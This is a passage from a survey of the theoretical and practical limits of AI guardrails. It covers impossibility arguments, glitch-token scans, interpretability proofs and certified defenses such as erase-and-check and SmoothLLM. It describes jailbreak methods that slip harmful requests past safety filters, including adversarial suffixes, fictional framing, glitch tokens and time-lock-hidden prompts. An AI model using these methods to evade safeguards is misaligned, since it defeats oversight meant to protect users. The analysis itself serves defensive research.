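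Vassilev gives "x is an adversarial prompt that Π deems unacceptable" as an example of a statement for a checker. An unprovable true statement of that kind would come closer to supporting the conclusion, but the proof does not produce one.

The search in step 3 also makes too strong an assumption, that a program can list the forbidden prompts in order of length. Anyone with such a program could filter perfectly by listing the forbidden prompts up to the length of each new prompt and checking whether that prompt is among them. The proof can avoid this assumption by searching through all strings instead of only the forbidden ones. The theorem then still holds, but it is still about program length.

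Vassilev gives a separate, informal argument from the ambiguity of language. A request to explain how people break the encryption that banks use could come from a historian, a student of cryptography or a thief, and the words alone may not show which. This is a real difficulty for guardrails, similar to the problem of specifying what an email assistant should do, but it does not depend on Gödel. A finite set of rules can sometimes cover limitless disguises, as one firewall rule covered every spelling of the Log4Shell string. Vassilev's point that the rules are finite and the possible disguises limitless is therefore not enough to prove that some prompt will get through.

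Two other papers apply similar ideas to compliance itself. Hasan (2026), in *Incompleteness of AI Safety Verification via Kolmogorov Complexity*, proves that any fixed verifier that never approves a violation must fail to certify some compliant behaviours once they are complex enough. Pérez-Acle (2026), in *No finite rulebook can certify every safe program*, considers a gatekeeper that reads programs written by an AI agent and decides whether to run them. Any correct rulebook of n bits fails to certify some compliant program of about n bits. Both results concern harmless cases that a verifier cannot approve, so an operator who blocks everything without a certificate would refuse some safe programs but would not let a harmful one through.

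### When a perfect guardrail is impossible

Published criticism of Vassilev's proof is scarce. Help Net Security repeated NIST's interpretation in *Every set of AI guardrails can be broken by the right prompt*. Amer, Kinczel and Long (2026) review several earlier limits on filtering in *No Perfect Guardrail & No Perfect Guard* without discussing Vassilev's, but they prove a theorem about right and wrong verdicts.

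A guard is exact if it blocks every forbidden output and passes every permitted one. For a model that can produce every finite string, an exact guard exists if and only if the policy is decidable, which means that some program always finishes and correctly determines whether the policy forbids a given string. Such a program is itself an exact guard. Conversely, anyone with an exact guard can decide the policy. To check a string, they run the model on one prompt after another, with every possible set of random choices, until it produces that string, and then see whether the guard blocks it.

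If the policy is undecidable, every guard makes infinitely many errors. If a guard made only finitely many, adding a list of corrections would make it exact, and no guard can be exact for an undecidable policy.

This theorem also covers the guardrail that blocks everything. Such a guardrail is useless, but no jailbreak can get past it, so NIST's claim that some prompt will always work is false for it. Vassilev's definition of alignment excludes it by requiring an aligned system to process acceptable prompts, but his proof never uses this requirement. Amer and colleagues exclude it by requiring an exact guard to pass whatever the policy permits. They also show that, for an undecidable policy, any guard that blocks every forbidden output must block infinitely many permitted ones, so the organisation has to accept either that or some forbidden outputs getting through.

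### A fixed context window

Step 1 requires prompts of unlimited length, but real models have a fixed context window. Vassilev offers a second theorem for this case. In one part of its two-part proof, short programs can output every forbidden prompt, so the statement about program length is false for all of them. Vassilev says the theorem holds here because the checker never accepts the statement. But a checker is supposed to reject false statements, and the theorem requires a true statement that the checker never accepts.

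The other part requires a forbidden prompt that no program of n bits or less can output. A program can always store a prompt and print it, so n has to be smaller than the longest possible prompt, apart from a small constant. For GPT-5's input limit of 272,000 tokens, the longest prompt is about 4.8 million bits. The search program also has to be shorter than n bits, and it contains the checker, so many guardrails are far too large. Llama Guard 4, Meta's filter model, has about 12 billion parameters, the numbers it learns in training (Ball, Gluch and colleagues, 2026, *Computational Barriers to Filtering for AI Alignment*). Even at one bit each, they would be 2,500 times as large as the longest prompt, so no value of n works. The argument could work with a very small checker, but the unprovable statement would still be about program length.

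A fixed limit on prompt length also removes the obstacle that Amer and colleagues describe. Every finite set is decidable, so an exact guard exists in principle, although no general method constructs it for every limit. Vassilev's argument then supports only the practical observation that such a window allows too many strings to test.

### Judging text by its meaning

Glukhov, Shumailov and colleagues (2023), in *LLM Censorship*, show that some rules about meaning are undecidable. Their first result covers text that describes a computer program, when the rule is about what the program does, such as a ban on malware. It relies on Henry Rice's 1953 theorem that if some programs have a certain behaviour and others do not, no algorithm can tell for every program whether it has that behaviour.

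A program may do something forbidden only after a long calculation, so predicting whether it is harmful means predicting whether the calculation ever ends. Pérez-Acle gives the example of a program that searches for an even number greater than two that is not the sum of two primes, and opens a safe if it finds one. The program is harmless if and only if Goldbach's conjecture is true, which mathematicians had not settled when the paper appeared in November 2026. The program appears harmless in every test of up to a million steps.

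Glukhov and colleagues acknowledge that Rice's theorem does not strictly apply to real systems, because computers have limited memory and models have limited inputs and outputs. These limits make it possible to determine whether a program follows a rule, but doing so may still take a lot of computation. Pérez-Acle proves that if a rule covers only the first T steps of a program, any checker that is always correct must spend nearly T steps on some programs.

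The second result of Glukhov and colleagues does apply to outputs of limited length. It assumes that a model can encode its answer in any way the user requests, and that an encoded answer is as harmful as the original if the user can decode it. A filter that checks only the output, without information about which codes the user knows, cannot determine whether an ordinary sentence is an encoded version of a forbidden one, so it must allow everything or forbid everything.

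This conclusion assumes that the user might know any conceivable code. An arbitrary code that turns a remark about the weather into a page of dangerous instructions would itself have to contain most of those instructions, so a user who had it would hardly need the model. The argument is more convincing for ordinary encryption with a short key, but then the user often has to tell the model how to encode the answer. An input filter might notice this, and Glukhov and colleagues state that their second result does not cover input filters. Amer and colleagues find that exact guards exist for limited outputs. They explain that this is compatible with Glukhov's result because their own policies are fixed sets of strings, while in Glukhov's result the status of a string depends on what its recipient can decode.

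Glukhov and colleagues also point out that an attacker can request harmless pieces of a harmful answer in separate conversations and assemble them afterwards. No filter that judges one answer at a time can prevent this. In *Position*, a later version of the work, they propose rules about the form of a text instead of its meaning, which can provide guarantees. The strictest such rule allows only outputs from an approved list, which makes the model much less useful.

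### Filters weaker than the model

Even where a perfect filter exists, it may take too long to run. *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* (Ball, Gluch and colleagues, 2025) proves a result of this kind for filters that have much less computing time than the model they protect. The result applies to filters that accept harmless prompts with high probability, which excludes a filter that blocks everything.

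The proof relies on time-lock puzzles, which a sender can create quickly but which take a long, predictable amount of computation to solve. In one type, the solver squares a number, keeps the remainder after dividing by a very large number N, and repeats this t times. N is the product of two primes, and the person who created N knows them and can use them to take a shortcut. Cryptographers believe, but have not proved, that there is no substantially faster way for anyone who doesn't know the primes.

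Ball and colleagues then construct a special model that looks for such puzzles in its prompts, solves them and obeys any instruction inside. They show that an attacker can hide a harmful request in a puzzle, and hide the puzzle in a prompt that reads like a harmless one. The model has time to solve the puzzle, but if the assumption about time-lock puzzles is correct, a filter without that time cannot tell such prompts from harmless ones.

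MIT's lecture notes on the result (2026) give a formula for the gap in computing time. If the model runs for t steps, the filter gets t^ε steps, where ε is a fixed number between 0 and 1. If ε is one half, a filter for a model that takes a trillion steps would get a million.

The theorem shows that a filter of this kind fails for some model, but not that it fails for any model now in use. Ball and colleagues concede in their 2025 paper that the constructed model's behaviour may be contrived. In the later conference version, they reply that an outside body that cannot see a model's internal workings needs a filter that is reliable for every model, so one counterexample is enough. That is a good argument against a regulator's universal filter, but a weaker one against a filter that a company builds for its own model, because the company can study both. The result does not apply to an input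 filter with as much computing time as the model, although such a filter would be expensive to run and would itself need to be trustworthy.

Ball and colleagues' proof about output filters holds even if the filter runs for longer than the model. It assumes that working out whether an answer is harmful can take far longer than either program runs. Their example is a complex business plan that cuts costs by subtly excluding certain clients. They agree that an output filter is easy to build where harm is easy to recognise.

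### How rare and how costly the failures are

Vassilev's proof does not identify any prompt that gets past a guardrail, or estimate how many such prompts exist or how long an attacker would need to find one. A tester therefore cannot use it to predict an attack success rate or decide how many prompts to try.

Amer and colleagues show that, for any fixed pattern of use, a guard can be wrong about infinitely many outputs and still be right almost all the time. Some finite collection of outputs covers, say, 99.99% of what the model produces. A guard that passes only the permitted outputs in this collection never lets a forbidden output through, and it wrongly blocks a permitted one at most about once in 10,000 uses. Such a guard exists even for an undecidable policy, though no single algorithm can construct one for every collection.

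The proof that this guard exists does not help anyone build one for a real system, but it shows that the theorem sets no minimum on the average error. Pérez-Acle reaches a similar conclusion from simulations of 2.2 million random programs. Programs that defeat a gatekeeper are mostly written by an adversary and rarely come up by chance.

A low average error is weak evidence of safety against attackers, who choose their inputs. Amer and colleagues give α × σ × λ as a lower bound on the expected loss per use, where α is the share of uses that come from an attacker, σ is the attacker's chance of getting a forbidden output past the guard, and λ is the smallest loss such an output causes. If one use in 1,000 comes from an attacker, attackers succeed half the time, and each success causes at least $10,000 of damage, the expected loss is at least $5 per use, however well the guard handles everyone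 else. The limit theorems do not provide values for α, σ or λ.

Amer and colleagues advise against requiring that a system never produce a kind of harmful output defined by its meaning or effect. They recommend that requirements instead state a tolerated error rate, which testers can measure, and the pattern of use and type of attacker it applies to.

### What NIST recommends

NIST's announcement recommends that red teams search constantly for new attack prompts, that developers keep updating their guardrails against the prompts these teams find, and that organisations prepare to limit the damage and recover quickly when an attack succeeds. Vassilev wants to reach a point where "the cost of finding new exploits exceeds attackers' resources".

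If the theorem did establish that every finite set of guardrails has a gap, no organisation could install guardrails once and consider the job finished. Updates would not necessarily help, because an updated set is still finite and the theorem would still apply. Vassilev makes a similar point about Gödel's theorem, where adding statements to a theory to fix one problem leads to another, and the article claims only that updates may be effective. The theorem of Amer and colleagues better supports continuing to search for errors, because it shows that when a policy is undecidable and a model can produce any string, correcting errors one at a time always leaves infinitely many.

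Updating guardrails is useful in practice because many attackers reuse methods that are already public, as they did with the Log4Shell vulnerability, and even a simple rule stops some of these attacks. A new rule can also block prompts other than the one it was written for, although a rule that is too broad will block legitimate requests.

An organisation whose guardrails might fail has reason to prepare for successful attacks by limiting an agent's permissions and keeping backups, whether or not a perfect guardrail is possible in theory.

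The goal of making attacks too expensive rests on a judgement about economics. Vassilev compares new attack prompts to undiscovered flaws in ordinary software, which often took a government's resources to find and exploit. But a language model accepts ordinary language, so the search may be much cheaper. Vassilev also warns that a flaw in one company's system is usually soon used against other companies with the same flaw. This makes it harder to make attacks too expensive, because an attacker who spent $50,000 on a prompt that worked against 100 companies would have paid only $500 for each. Finding out whether a particular defence is expensive enough to break requires testing it with attackers who adapt to it.

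## Input spaces small enough to test completely

A tester can try every one-token prompt in minutes. Researchers have done this to look for tokens that make a model behave erratically. Others have trained a small model with fewer than 17 million possible inputs in total.

### Tokens that a model has hardly seen

Developers usually build the tokenizer separately, from a smaller body of text than the model's training data. If the two differ, the vocabulary can contain tokens that rarely or never appear in the training data. When asked to repeat one of these under-trained tokens, or "glitch tokens", a model may produce a different word or garbled text. A well-known example is " SolidGoldMagikarp", from GPT-2's vocabulary.

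Land and Bartolo (2024), in *Fishing for Magikarp*, traced some of these tokens to their origin. The developers of StarCoder2, a programming model, published the text used to train its tokenizer. A single document in that text, which demonstrated very long variable names in Java, produced several tokens of Latin filler text. Byte pair encoding also leaves fragments behind. GPT-2's vocabulary contains " TheNitromeFan", one of several tokens that come from user names, and " TheNitrome", which the tokenizer made as a step toward the longer token and seldom uses by itself.

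To find such tokens, Land and Bartolo first scored the whole vocabulary without running the model. A model stores a list of numbers, called an embedding, for each token and adjusts it during training. If a token never appears in the training text, its input embedding changes only through weight decay, which shrinks a model's numbers towards zero. An embedding close to zero is therefore a sign of an under-trained token. Some models use the same embeddings to read tokens and to choose output tokens. For these models, Land and Bartolo measured how closely each embedding resembled those of tokens known to be unused.

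Land and Bartolo then prompted the model with the most suspicious 2% of tokens. Three prompts strongly encouraged it to repeat each token, for example by showing it many identical repetitions. They counted a token as under-trained if the model always gave it a probability below 1%.

| Model | Vocabulary | Tokens prompted | Confirmed as under-trained | Share of vocabulary |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-2 XL | 50,257 | 999 | 67 | 0.13% |
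| GPT-J 6B | 50,400 | 999 | 200 | 0.40% |
| GPT-NeoX 20B | 50,277 | 993 | 10 | 0.02% |
| Llama 3 8B | 128,256 | 2,540 | 556 | 0.43% |
| Qwen1.5 32B | 151,646 | 2,966 | 2,450 | 1.6% |
| Gemma 2B | 256,000 | 5,117 | 3,161 | 1.2% |
| Gemma 7B | 256,000 | 5,117 | 800 | 0.31% |

GPT-J uses GPT-2's tokenizer but was trained on different text, and it has three times as many under-trained tokens as GPT-2 XL. GPT-NeoX has very few, probably because its developers built the tokenizer from the model's training data. OLMo, another open model, uses the same tokenizer as GPT-NeoX but was trained on other data, and it has more than 170.

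For OLMo, Land and Bartolo also prompted the model with all 49,575 tokens that they could test. They found 191 under-trained tokens. The 2% shortcut had caught 175 of these, missing about one in twelve, with a fiftieth of the prompts. For Qwen1.5 32B, 83% of the tokens they prompted were under-trained, so the shortcut probably missed many others. Another shortcut, in *Glitch Tokens in Large Language Models* (2024), looks for clusters of similar embeddings. It needed 73% fewer queries than an exhaustive search but found only 63% of the glitch tokens on average. A vocabulary is small enough that testers can avoid these misses by prompting with every token.

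### Newer models and stricter tests

A new tokenizer removes old glitch tokens and can bring in new ones. After identifying glitch tokens in open models, Land and Bartolo found that OpenAI's models before GPT-4o, which used the same tokenizer, mishandled many of them. GPT-4o has a different tokenizer, and some of its under-trained tokens apparently come from Chinese advertisements. Some of the suspect tokens caused trouble in Claude 2.1, but none did in the Claude 3 models.

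Tang, Qi and colleagues (2026) showed in *One Bad Token Spoils the Barrel* that glitch tokens can also get past a model's safety mechanisms, and that a token that disturbs one model often disturbs others. They reported their findings to nine companies, including OpenAI and Anthropic.

Many of the same researchers later tested every token in the vocabularies of ten models in *GlitchPatch* (Tang, Qi and colleagues, 2026). They asked each model to repeat each token, spell it and count its characters, and labelled it a glitch token if the model failed any task. The share of glitch tokens ranged from 11.9% for Qwen3.8-27B to 19.5% for Mistral 7B. They counted 22,026 in Llama 3.1 8B, about 40 times as many as Land and Bartolo found in Llama 3 8B.

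Most of that difference probably comes from the definition. Land and Bartolo counted only tokens that a model could hardly produce, but a model can produce a token easily and still get its spelling wrong. For 15% to 29% of the tokens that Tang and colleagues labelled as glitches, the models failed only the counting task. Each task has an exact right answer, so a computer can serve as the test oracle, but the number of failures still depends on which tasks the testers choose.

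A complete test also reveals the side effects of a repair. One way to repair a glitch token is to delete the rule that creates it, so that the tokenizer splits the text into smaller, better-known tokens. Tang and colleagues tried this on Qwen3.8-27B and repaired 41% of its glitch tokens, but 6.5% of its normal tokens then failed, and the total number of failures rose. For example, deleting the rule for "rastructure" also stopped the tokenizer from forming "Infrastructure". Their own method replaces only the glitch token itself, with other tokens that spell the same text. It repaired 85% of glitch tokens on average without harming any normal ones.

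### Why single tokens do not settle pairs

Llama 3.1's 128,256 tokens make 16.4 billion pairs. Running the three tasks on all of them would take about a year and a half at 1,000 prompts a second, so a full scan is practical only for single tokens. Passing that scan does not guarantee that a model will handle pairs correctly, because it can handle two tokens well separately and fail when they are next to each other.

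To repair glitch tokens, Tang and colleagues built replacement sequences only from tokens that had passed all three tasks, yet they still had to test each sequence as a whole. When their ranking did not include how well adjacent tokens work together, the share of glitch tokens they could repair in Qwen3.8-27B fell from 87.5% to 81.7%.

*Improbable Bigrams Expose Vulnerabilities of Incomplete Tokens in Byte-Level Tokenizers* (Jang, Lee and colleagues, 2024) searched directly for bad token pairs. Computers store many non-Latin characters as two or three bytes, and byte pair encoding can create a token that begins or ends partway through a character. Llama 3.1 has 1,224 of these incomplete tokens. Land and Bartolo left such tokens out of their prompts because the tokens are not readable on their own.

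Jang and colleagues kept only incomplete tokens from the better-trained half of each vocabulary, as measured by Land and Bartolo's scores. They joined these tokens into pairs that formed characters from two different writing systems, which a model is unlikely to have seen together. A model failed on a pair only if it could not repeat it in any of four prompts. Llama 3.1 failed on 48 of 100 such pairs and on none of 100 pairs of complete tokens with similar scores. Across five models, the failure rate for pairs of incomplete tokens ranged from 33% to 77%. Splitting the same text into different tokens reduced Llama's failure rate to 5%, so the pairs of tokens caused most of its failures, not the characters themselves. Splitting the text differently did not help Command R, whose vocabulary is about twice as large as Llama's.

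Llama 3.1 has only about 71,000 possible pairs of incomplete tokens. Testing each pair in four prompts would take less than five minutes at 1,000 prompts a second. Jang and colleagues tested at most 100 pairs per model, but their work shows how a tester who knows which pairs are suspect could check them all.

Testers often lack such knowledge. The post *Opus 5 Glitch Text* reports that a short phrase of everyday words, followed by a dash, made Claude Opus 5 give very strange responses. The post suggests that the model may have been trying to complete the prompt instead of answering it. Nothing about the individual tokens would have led a tester to that phrase.

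### A model with 16.8 million inputs

In *Compact Proofs of Model Performance via Mechanistic Interpretability*, Gross, Agrawal and colleagues (2024) trained 151 models, each from a different random starting point, to read four whole numbers between 0 and 63 and output the largest. With 64 possible tokens in each of four positions, there are 64^4 = 16,777,216 inputs. Gross and colleagues chose four positions because that was the longest input for which they could feasibly test every possibility.

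The models are transformers, the design behind most language models, but they have only one layer and none of the other components that large models have. Running a model on every input proves its exact accuracy, which averaged 99.92% across the models, or about 13,000 wrong answers per model. This brute-force proof takes about 2^47 (140 trillion) arithmetic operations, and a fifth input position would multiply the number of inputs by 64.

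Gross and colleagues then looked for shorter proofs, using mechanistic interpretability, the study of how a model's internal numbers produce its behaviour. At the last position, the model gives the four tokens weights that add up to one. Each token contributes to the model's scores for the 64 possible answers in proportion to its weight. They found that a token's weight depends almost entirely on the size of its number, and grows about 3.4 times larger each time the number goes up by one. For the input 5, 40, 12, 39, the number 40 gets about 77% of the weight and 39 gets nearly all the rest. The model copies the tokens with the most weight, so 40 receives the highest score.

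### Shorter proofs and weaker guarantees

This structure lets one check cover many inputs. Because the scores are a weighted average, an input with several different small numbers is in effect a mixture of inputs that each contain only one of them. In the example, the largest number is 40 and the last is 39. If the model is right on the inputs made from 40, 39 and 5, and on those made from 40, 39 and 12, it must also be right on inputs that mix the 5 and the 12. The proof therefore needs to consider only combinations of three numbers, of which there are at most 64^3 = 262,144. It assumes the least favourable order for each.

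This proof takes about 2^25 operations, four million times fewer than brute force. On average, it guarantees an accuracy of at least 95.3%. The remaining 4.7% is nearly 800,000 inputs, about 60 times as many as an average model gets wrong. If one of the simpler inputs fails its check, the proof gives no guarantee for the original input, even if the model answers it correctly.

Even shorter proofs don't check combinations of three numbers. They work out the worst case for each part of the model separately and add the results, but these worst cases may never occur together. Suppose one part contributes 10 when the largest number is even and 0 when it is odd, and another part does the reverse. The total is always 10, but adding the two minimums gives 0. Gross and colleagues reduce this gap by moving the average effect of one part into the other before taking the minimums.

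With that adjustment, one such proof takes about 2^21 operations, a sixteenth as many as the proof from three-number inputs, and guarantees 70.2% accuracy. Without the adjustment, it guarantees only 34.9%. Some of the 102 proof strategies guarantee almost nothing. The guarantees were tighter for models whose internal numbers more closely matched the simplified description, so a guarantee's size also measures how well the researchers understand the model.

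### Why the proofs are hard to scale

Gross and colleagues have to assume in their proof that anything they cannot explain about a model always does the most harm it could. They call these unexplained parts structureless noise. In one attempt, they simplified each of several tables of numbers that the model multiplies together. Each simplification introduced only a small error, but they did not know how the errors combined. Assuming the worst gave a bound far larger than the real error, which made the guarantee worthless. They suspect that there is often no short explanation of why such errors stay small in practice.

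The difficulty grows with the number of layers. If each layer could at most double an error, a proof that assumes the worst case at every layer would have to allow for the error growing about a billionfold over 30 layers, even if the real model hardly changed it.

Testing a sample of inputs cannot rule out failures on the rest, as with Dijkstra's multiplier. *Certification from Examples is Hard for Circuits and Transformers under Minimal Overparametrization* (2026) proves that certifying a network from examples can take exponentially many of them when the set of possible networks is even slightly larger than it needs to be.

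Later attempts have met similar limits:

- *Towards a unified and verified understanding of group-operation networks* (2024) applied the method to 100 small networks that combine two rearrangements of five objects. A proof based on the researchers' explanation guaranteed nearly 100% accuracy for about half of the networks and 0% for the other half. Many of the latter turned out not to work as the explanation said.
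- *Interactions between crosscoder features* (2026) tried to remove the need to write each proof by hand, using a tool that breaks a model's internal activity into simpler features. The researchers worked with a model of 33 million parameters that writes children's stories. They obtained meaningful guarantees for some components but not for the whole model, and they call the procedure "not yet practically applicable to large models".
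- *BlockCert* (2025) applies a computer-checked theorem to TinyLlama, a small language model. The theorem combines the errors of the model's separate blocks, but the researchers measured those errors instead of proving them, so the result is not a guarantee for every input.
- Somani (2026), in *Towards Verifiable Transformers*, used an automatic solver to check parts of a model that decide how to close quotation marks and brackets. This worked directly on small models. At the scale of GPT-2, Somani had to remove one component and replace parts of the model with short programs before the solver could verify it.

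### Menus and fixed forms

A language model of any size can have a small input space if the software around it accepts only certain inputs. Suppose a customer fills in a form with five menus of ten options each, and the software turns the choices into a prompt. There are only 100,000 possible prompts. Running each one 300 times to catch rare answers would take a little over eight hours at 1,000 runs a second. Adding a free-text box limited to two tokens would multiply the number of prompts by 40 billion.

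The test covers only the exact prompts that the software builds. A vocabulary scan has the same limit, because it tries each token in only a few fixed sentences. Land and Bartolo report that some tokens passed their test prompts but could still cause errors elsewhere.

The results of the arithmetic can also differ between computers, because computers round most calculations and adding the same numbers in a different order can give a slightly different sum. That difference might change an answer. *Spec2Weights* (2026) addresses this for small networks that a language model writes from a specification, including one for the Roman numerals from 1 to 3,999. It gives conditions under which a network's calculations are exact in any order, so that testing every input once amounts to a proof. For several of these networks, a simple format check is enough to reject any input the proof does not cover.

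## Erase-and-check: one guarantee for a whole family of prompts

A certificate can cover a set of prompts far too large to list if one argument applies to all of them, as Dijkstra's two cases did for every pair of numbers. *Certifying LLM Safety against Adversarial Prompting* (Kumar, Agarwal and colleagues, 2023) gave the first clear example for prompts. Its method, erase-and-check, covers every prompt that an attacker can make by adding a limited number of tokens to a harmful request.

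They designed erase-and-check to counter an attack that Andy Zou and colleagues published in 2023. The attack searches automatically for suffixes that make a model answer requests it would normally refuse. Suffixes of 20 tokens succeeded against GPT-3.5 in up to 84% of cases. Because the search can keep producing new suffixes, a list of known ones is soon out of date, as the early signatures for Log4Shell were.

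### Removing the added tokens

Suppose an attacker can append at most d tokens to a harmful request. The checker receives the longer prompt and does not know where the original request ends. It takes three steps:

1. It runs a safety filter on the whole prompt.
2. It removes the last token and runs the filter again, and repeats this until it has removed d tokens.
3. It labels the prompt harmful if the filter flagged any of these versions.

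If the attacker added seven tokens, removing the last seven gives back the original request. So if the filter flags the request by itself, erase-and-check also flags it with any suffix of up to d tokens. The original request serves as a normal form for this family, though prompts in general have none. The checker is sure to check it because it tries every suffix length up to d, which is far fewer cases than every possible suffix.

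With a vocabulary of 32,000 tokens and d = 20, there are 32,000^20, or about 10^90, possible 20-token suffixes. The checker covers these and all shorter suffixes with 21 filter calls.

To measure the guarantee, a tester only needs to run the filter on a set of harmful requests, without any attack prompts, and record the share it flags. Erase-and-check will flag at least that share of the same requests under any attack of this kind, including attacks nobody has invented yet. The argument also works for a filter whose answers are partly random. If the filter flags a request 90% of the time, erase-and-check flags every covered variant of that request at least 90% of the time.

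### When the tokens can go anywhere

An attacker might insert the extra tokens in the middle of the request. If they form a single block, the checker has to try removing every block of up to d consecutive tokens. If the attacker can scatter them, it has to try removing every combination of up to d tokens. The table gives the number of filter calls for d = 20. A 36-token prompt consists of a 16-token request, the average length in Kumar and colleagues' test set, and 20 added tokens.

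| Where the attacker adds up to 20 tokens | Filter calls for a 36-token prompt | Filter calls for a 1,000-token prompt |
|---|---|---|
| At the end | 21 | 21 |
| In one block anywhere | 531 | 19,811 |
| Scattered through the prompt | 55 billion | 3 × 10^41 |

At 1,000 calls a second, the scattered case would take about 1.7 years for the short prompt. Kumar and colleagues extend the method to several separate blocks, but each added block multiplies the work. For two blocks in a 36-token prompt, the checker would have to try up to about 140,000 pairs. The method has to cover every possible position of the attacker's tokens, though not every choice of tokens.

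### Two filters and their results

Kumar and colleagues built two versions of the safety filter. The first was Llama 2, a general language model from Meta, which they instructed to answer "harmful" or "not harmful". They told it to choose "not harmful" if a request was unclear or incomplete, because erasing tokens produces many broken sentences. The second was DistilBERT, a much smaller model, which they trained to classify requests. They included shortened versions of harmless prompts in its training data so that it would learn to classify those as harmless too.

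The harmful requests came from AdvBench, a collection of 520 requests that Zou and colleagues had written to test their attack. Llama 2 flagged 92% of them, so erase-and-check with this filter has a certified detection rate of 92%. DistilBERT flagged all 120 requests that Kumar and colleagues had excluded from its training and tuning. These figures apply to all three kinds of attack and every value of d.

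A longer search costs time and causes false alarms. Kumar and colleagues measured both on harmless prompts that ChatGPT had written. With up to 20 tokens removed from the end, the method passed 97% of these prompts with Llama 2 and 98% with DistilBERT. For the harder cases, DistilBERT gave the following results on one Nvidia A100 processor:

| Attack covered | Most tokens removed | Harmless prompts passed | Average time per prompt |
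|---|---|---|---|
| One block anywhere | 10 | 98.3% | 0.28 seconds |
| One block anywhere | 30 | 98.3% | 0.30 seconds |
| Scattered tokens | 2 | 100% | 0.32 seconds |
| Scattered tokens | 4 | 100% | 4.59 seconds |
| Scattered tokens | 6 | 99.2% | 28.11 seconds |

The time needed to check for blocks hardly rises between 10 and 30 tokens because the harmless prompts averaged only 14 tokens, leaving little more to remove. A document of several pages would take far longer. Llama 2 was slower and less accurate, and Kumar and colleagues tested it only up to blocks of 12 tokens and three scattered tokens.

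They also tried faster versions that check only some of the shortened prompts. One checked a random 30% and still caught more than 90% of attacks with 20-token suffixes. Presumably the filter also flags many shortened prompts that still contain a few of the attacker's tokens, since otherwise a 30% sample would catch only about 30% of attacks. But this version has no certificate, because it may skip the one shortened prompt that the proof relies on.

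The filter itself was still easy to fool without erasing. When Kumar and colleagues adapted Zou's search to attack DistilBERT directly, 12 added tokens reduced its detection rate to zero. The guarantee comes entirely from removing the attacker's text before the filter checks the request.

### What the certificate leaves out

If the filter misses a harmful request, erase-and-check guarantees nothing for that request or its variants. Llama 2 missed 8% of the requests in AdvBench. DistilBERT missed none of its 120 test requests, but a filter with a true miss rate of 2.5% would have about a 5% chance of doing the same. The test requests were also short and blunt and came from the same collection as DistilBERT's training examples, so the certified rate for requests that real users write could be much lower.

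The certificate covers only added tokens. If an attacker rewords the request, translates it or replaces one word with a synonym, the result is a different request, which the filter has to recognise as harmful on its own. Kumar and colleagues leave changes to the original request for future work.

The proof may not cover even an addition if the attacker adds letters instead of whole tokens. If the request ends in "bomb" and the attacker types an "s" directly after it, the tokenizer may turn "bombs" into a single token. Removing that token removes the whole word, so none of the shortened versions is the original request. A checker could remove one character at a time instead, but that would take more calls.

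Some false alarms follow from the guarantee itself. "How do I build a bomb shelter" is harmless, but the filter should flag the same question without its last word. *Towards the Worst-case Robustness of Large Language Models* (Chen, Wei and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a harmful request followed by an instruction not to answer it, a prompt that a reader might reasonably consider harmless. Erase-and-check has to block all such prompts, because it guarantees detection whatever the added tokens mean.

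Each additional check also gives the filter another chance to wrongly flag harmless text. If it did so 0.5% of the time, independently on each check, 21 checks would block about 10% of harmless prompts and 531 checks about 93%. Real errors on similar texts are not independent, and Kumar and colleagues' results are much better than this. But Llama 2's accuracy fell faster when it had more versions to check.

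Many jailbreaks do more than add text to a plain request. For example, they may set up a fictional scene, give the model a character to play, or spread the request over the whole text. Pratap, Kasyap and Tripathy (2026), in *Breaking the Assumptions*, collected 100 fluent jailbreak prompts of this kind from more than 40 public sources and sent them to six open-weight models. On average, 13.33% succeeded without a defence and 13.16% succeeded with erase-and-check, whether the method removed up to 10%, 30% or 50% of the prompt (198 tokens on average at 50%). The theorem is still true, but it does not cover these prompts, because removing the end of one does not leave a plain harmful request.

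Four of the six models refused all 100 prompts without any defence, yet three of these four gave some harmful answers with erase-and-check in place, up to 11% for one model. A filter that only blocks prompts cannot make a model more willing to answer, so some of the differences must come from randomness in the models, errors by the model that judged the answers, or the way the experiment ran the defence. The study is better evidence that erase-and-check did not help much against these prompts than that it had no effect.

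### Voting over altered copies

Smoothing is another way to obtain a certificate. A smoothing defence makes many randomly altered copies of a prompt, runs the model or filter on each, and combines the results, usually by majority vote. In *SmoothLLM*, Robey, Wong and colleagues (2023) used smoothing to protect a model directly. They had noticed that suffixes from automated searches are fragile. Some kinds of random change to 10% of a suffix's characters reduced the attack's success rate to below 1%. SmoothLLM therefore changes random characters throughout each copy of the prompt, collects the model's answers, and returns one from the winning side of the vote.

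Its certificate depends on an assumption, which is that the attack fails whenever at least k characters of the suffix change, for some number k. From k and the share of characters altered, Robey and colleagues calculate α, the probability that one altered copy gets a safe answer. The probability that at least half of N copies do is then

sum from t = N/2 to N of C(N, t) α^t (1 − α)^(N − t),

for even N, where C(N, t) is the number of ways to choose t copies out of N. With ten copies and α = 0.8, the defence succeeds 99.4% of the time. With α = 0.1, it succeeds only 0.2% of the time, which is worse than answering a single copy. The vote strengthens whichever result is already more common.

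Unlike the proof for erase-and-check, this one depends on an assumption about how the attack affects the model. *Towards Realistic Guarantees* (2025) reports that this assumption rarely holds. Attack success rates fall exponentially as more characters change, rather than dropping abruptly to zero. The paper makes a weaker assumption, that the attack fails with at least a certain probability once k characters have changed. That probability has to be estimated from known attacks, and a new type of attack could succeed more often after the same number of changes.

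SmoothLLM did not reduce the average success rate of fluent jailbreaks in tests by Pratap and colleagues. The rate went from 13.33% to 15.17%. For Phi-4, it rose from 24% to 38%. Pratap and colleagues suggest that the random characters made a borderline model less likely to recognise a request it should refuse. The rise for Phi-4 has a p-value of about 0.03, but the study made 30 such comparisons, so it could be chance.

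*Defending Large Language Models against Jailbreak Attacks via Semantic Smoothing* (2024) proposes voting over paraphrases and summaries instead, because random characters also damage ordinary prompts. This method has no certificate, and a faithful paraphrase of an attack written as a fictional scene preserves the attack. The average attack success rate in Pratap and colleagues' tests was 16%.

Kumar and colleagues explain why a majority vote gives a weaker guarantee than their rule. Suppose the attacker adds a 15-token suffix and the checker removes up to 20 tokens. Of the 21 versions, 15 still contain some of the attacker's text, and the filter might pass all of them. The other six are too few for a majority, but erase-and-check needs the filter to flag only one. They calculate that a vote over the same versions could never certify a suffix longer than ten tokens. Their rule is lopsided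 because they assume that nobody wants to make a harmless prompt look harmful. This is reasonable for a user attempting a jailbreak, but someone who sends text to another person's assistant might want the checker to block a harmless prompt.

### Certificates for changed words

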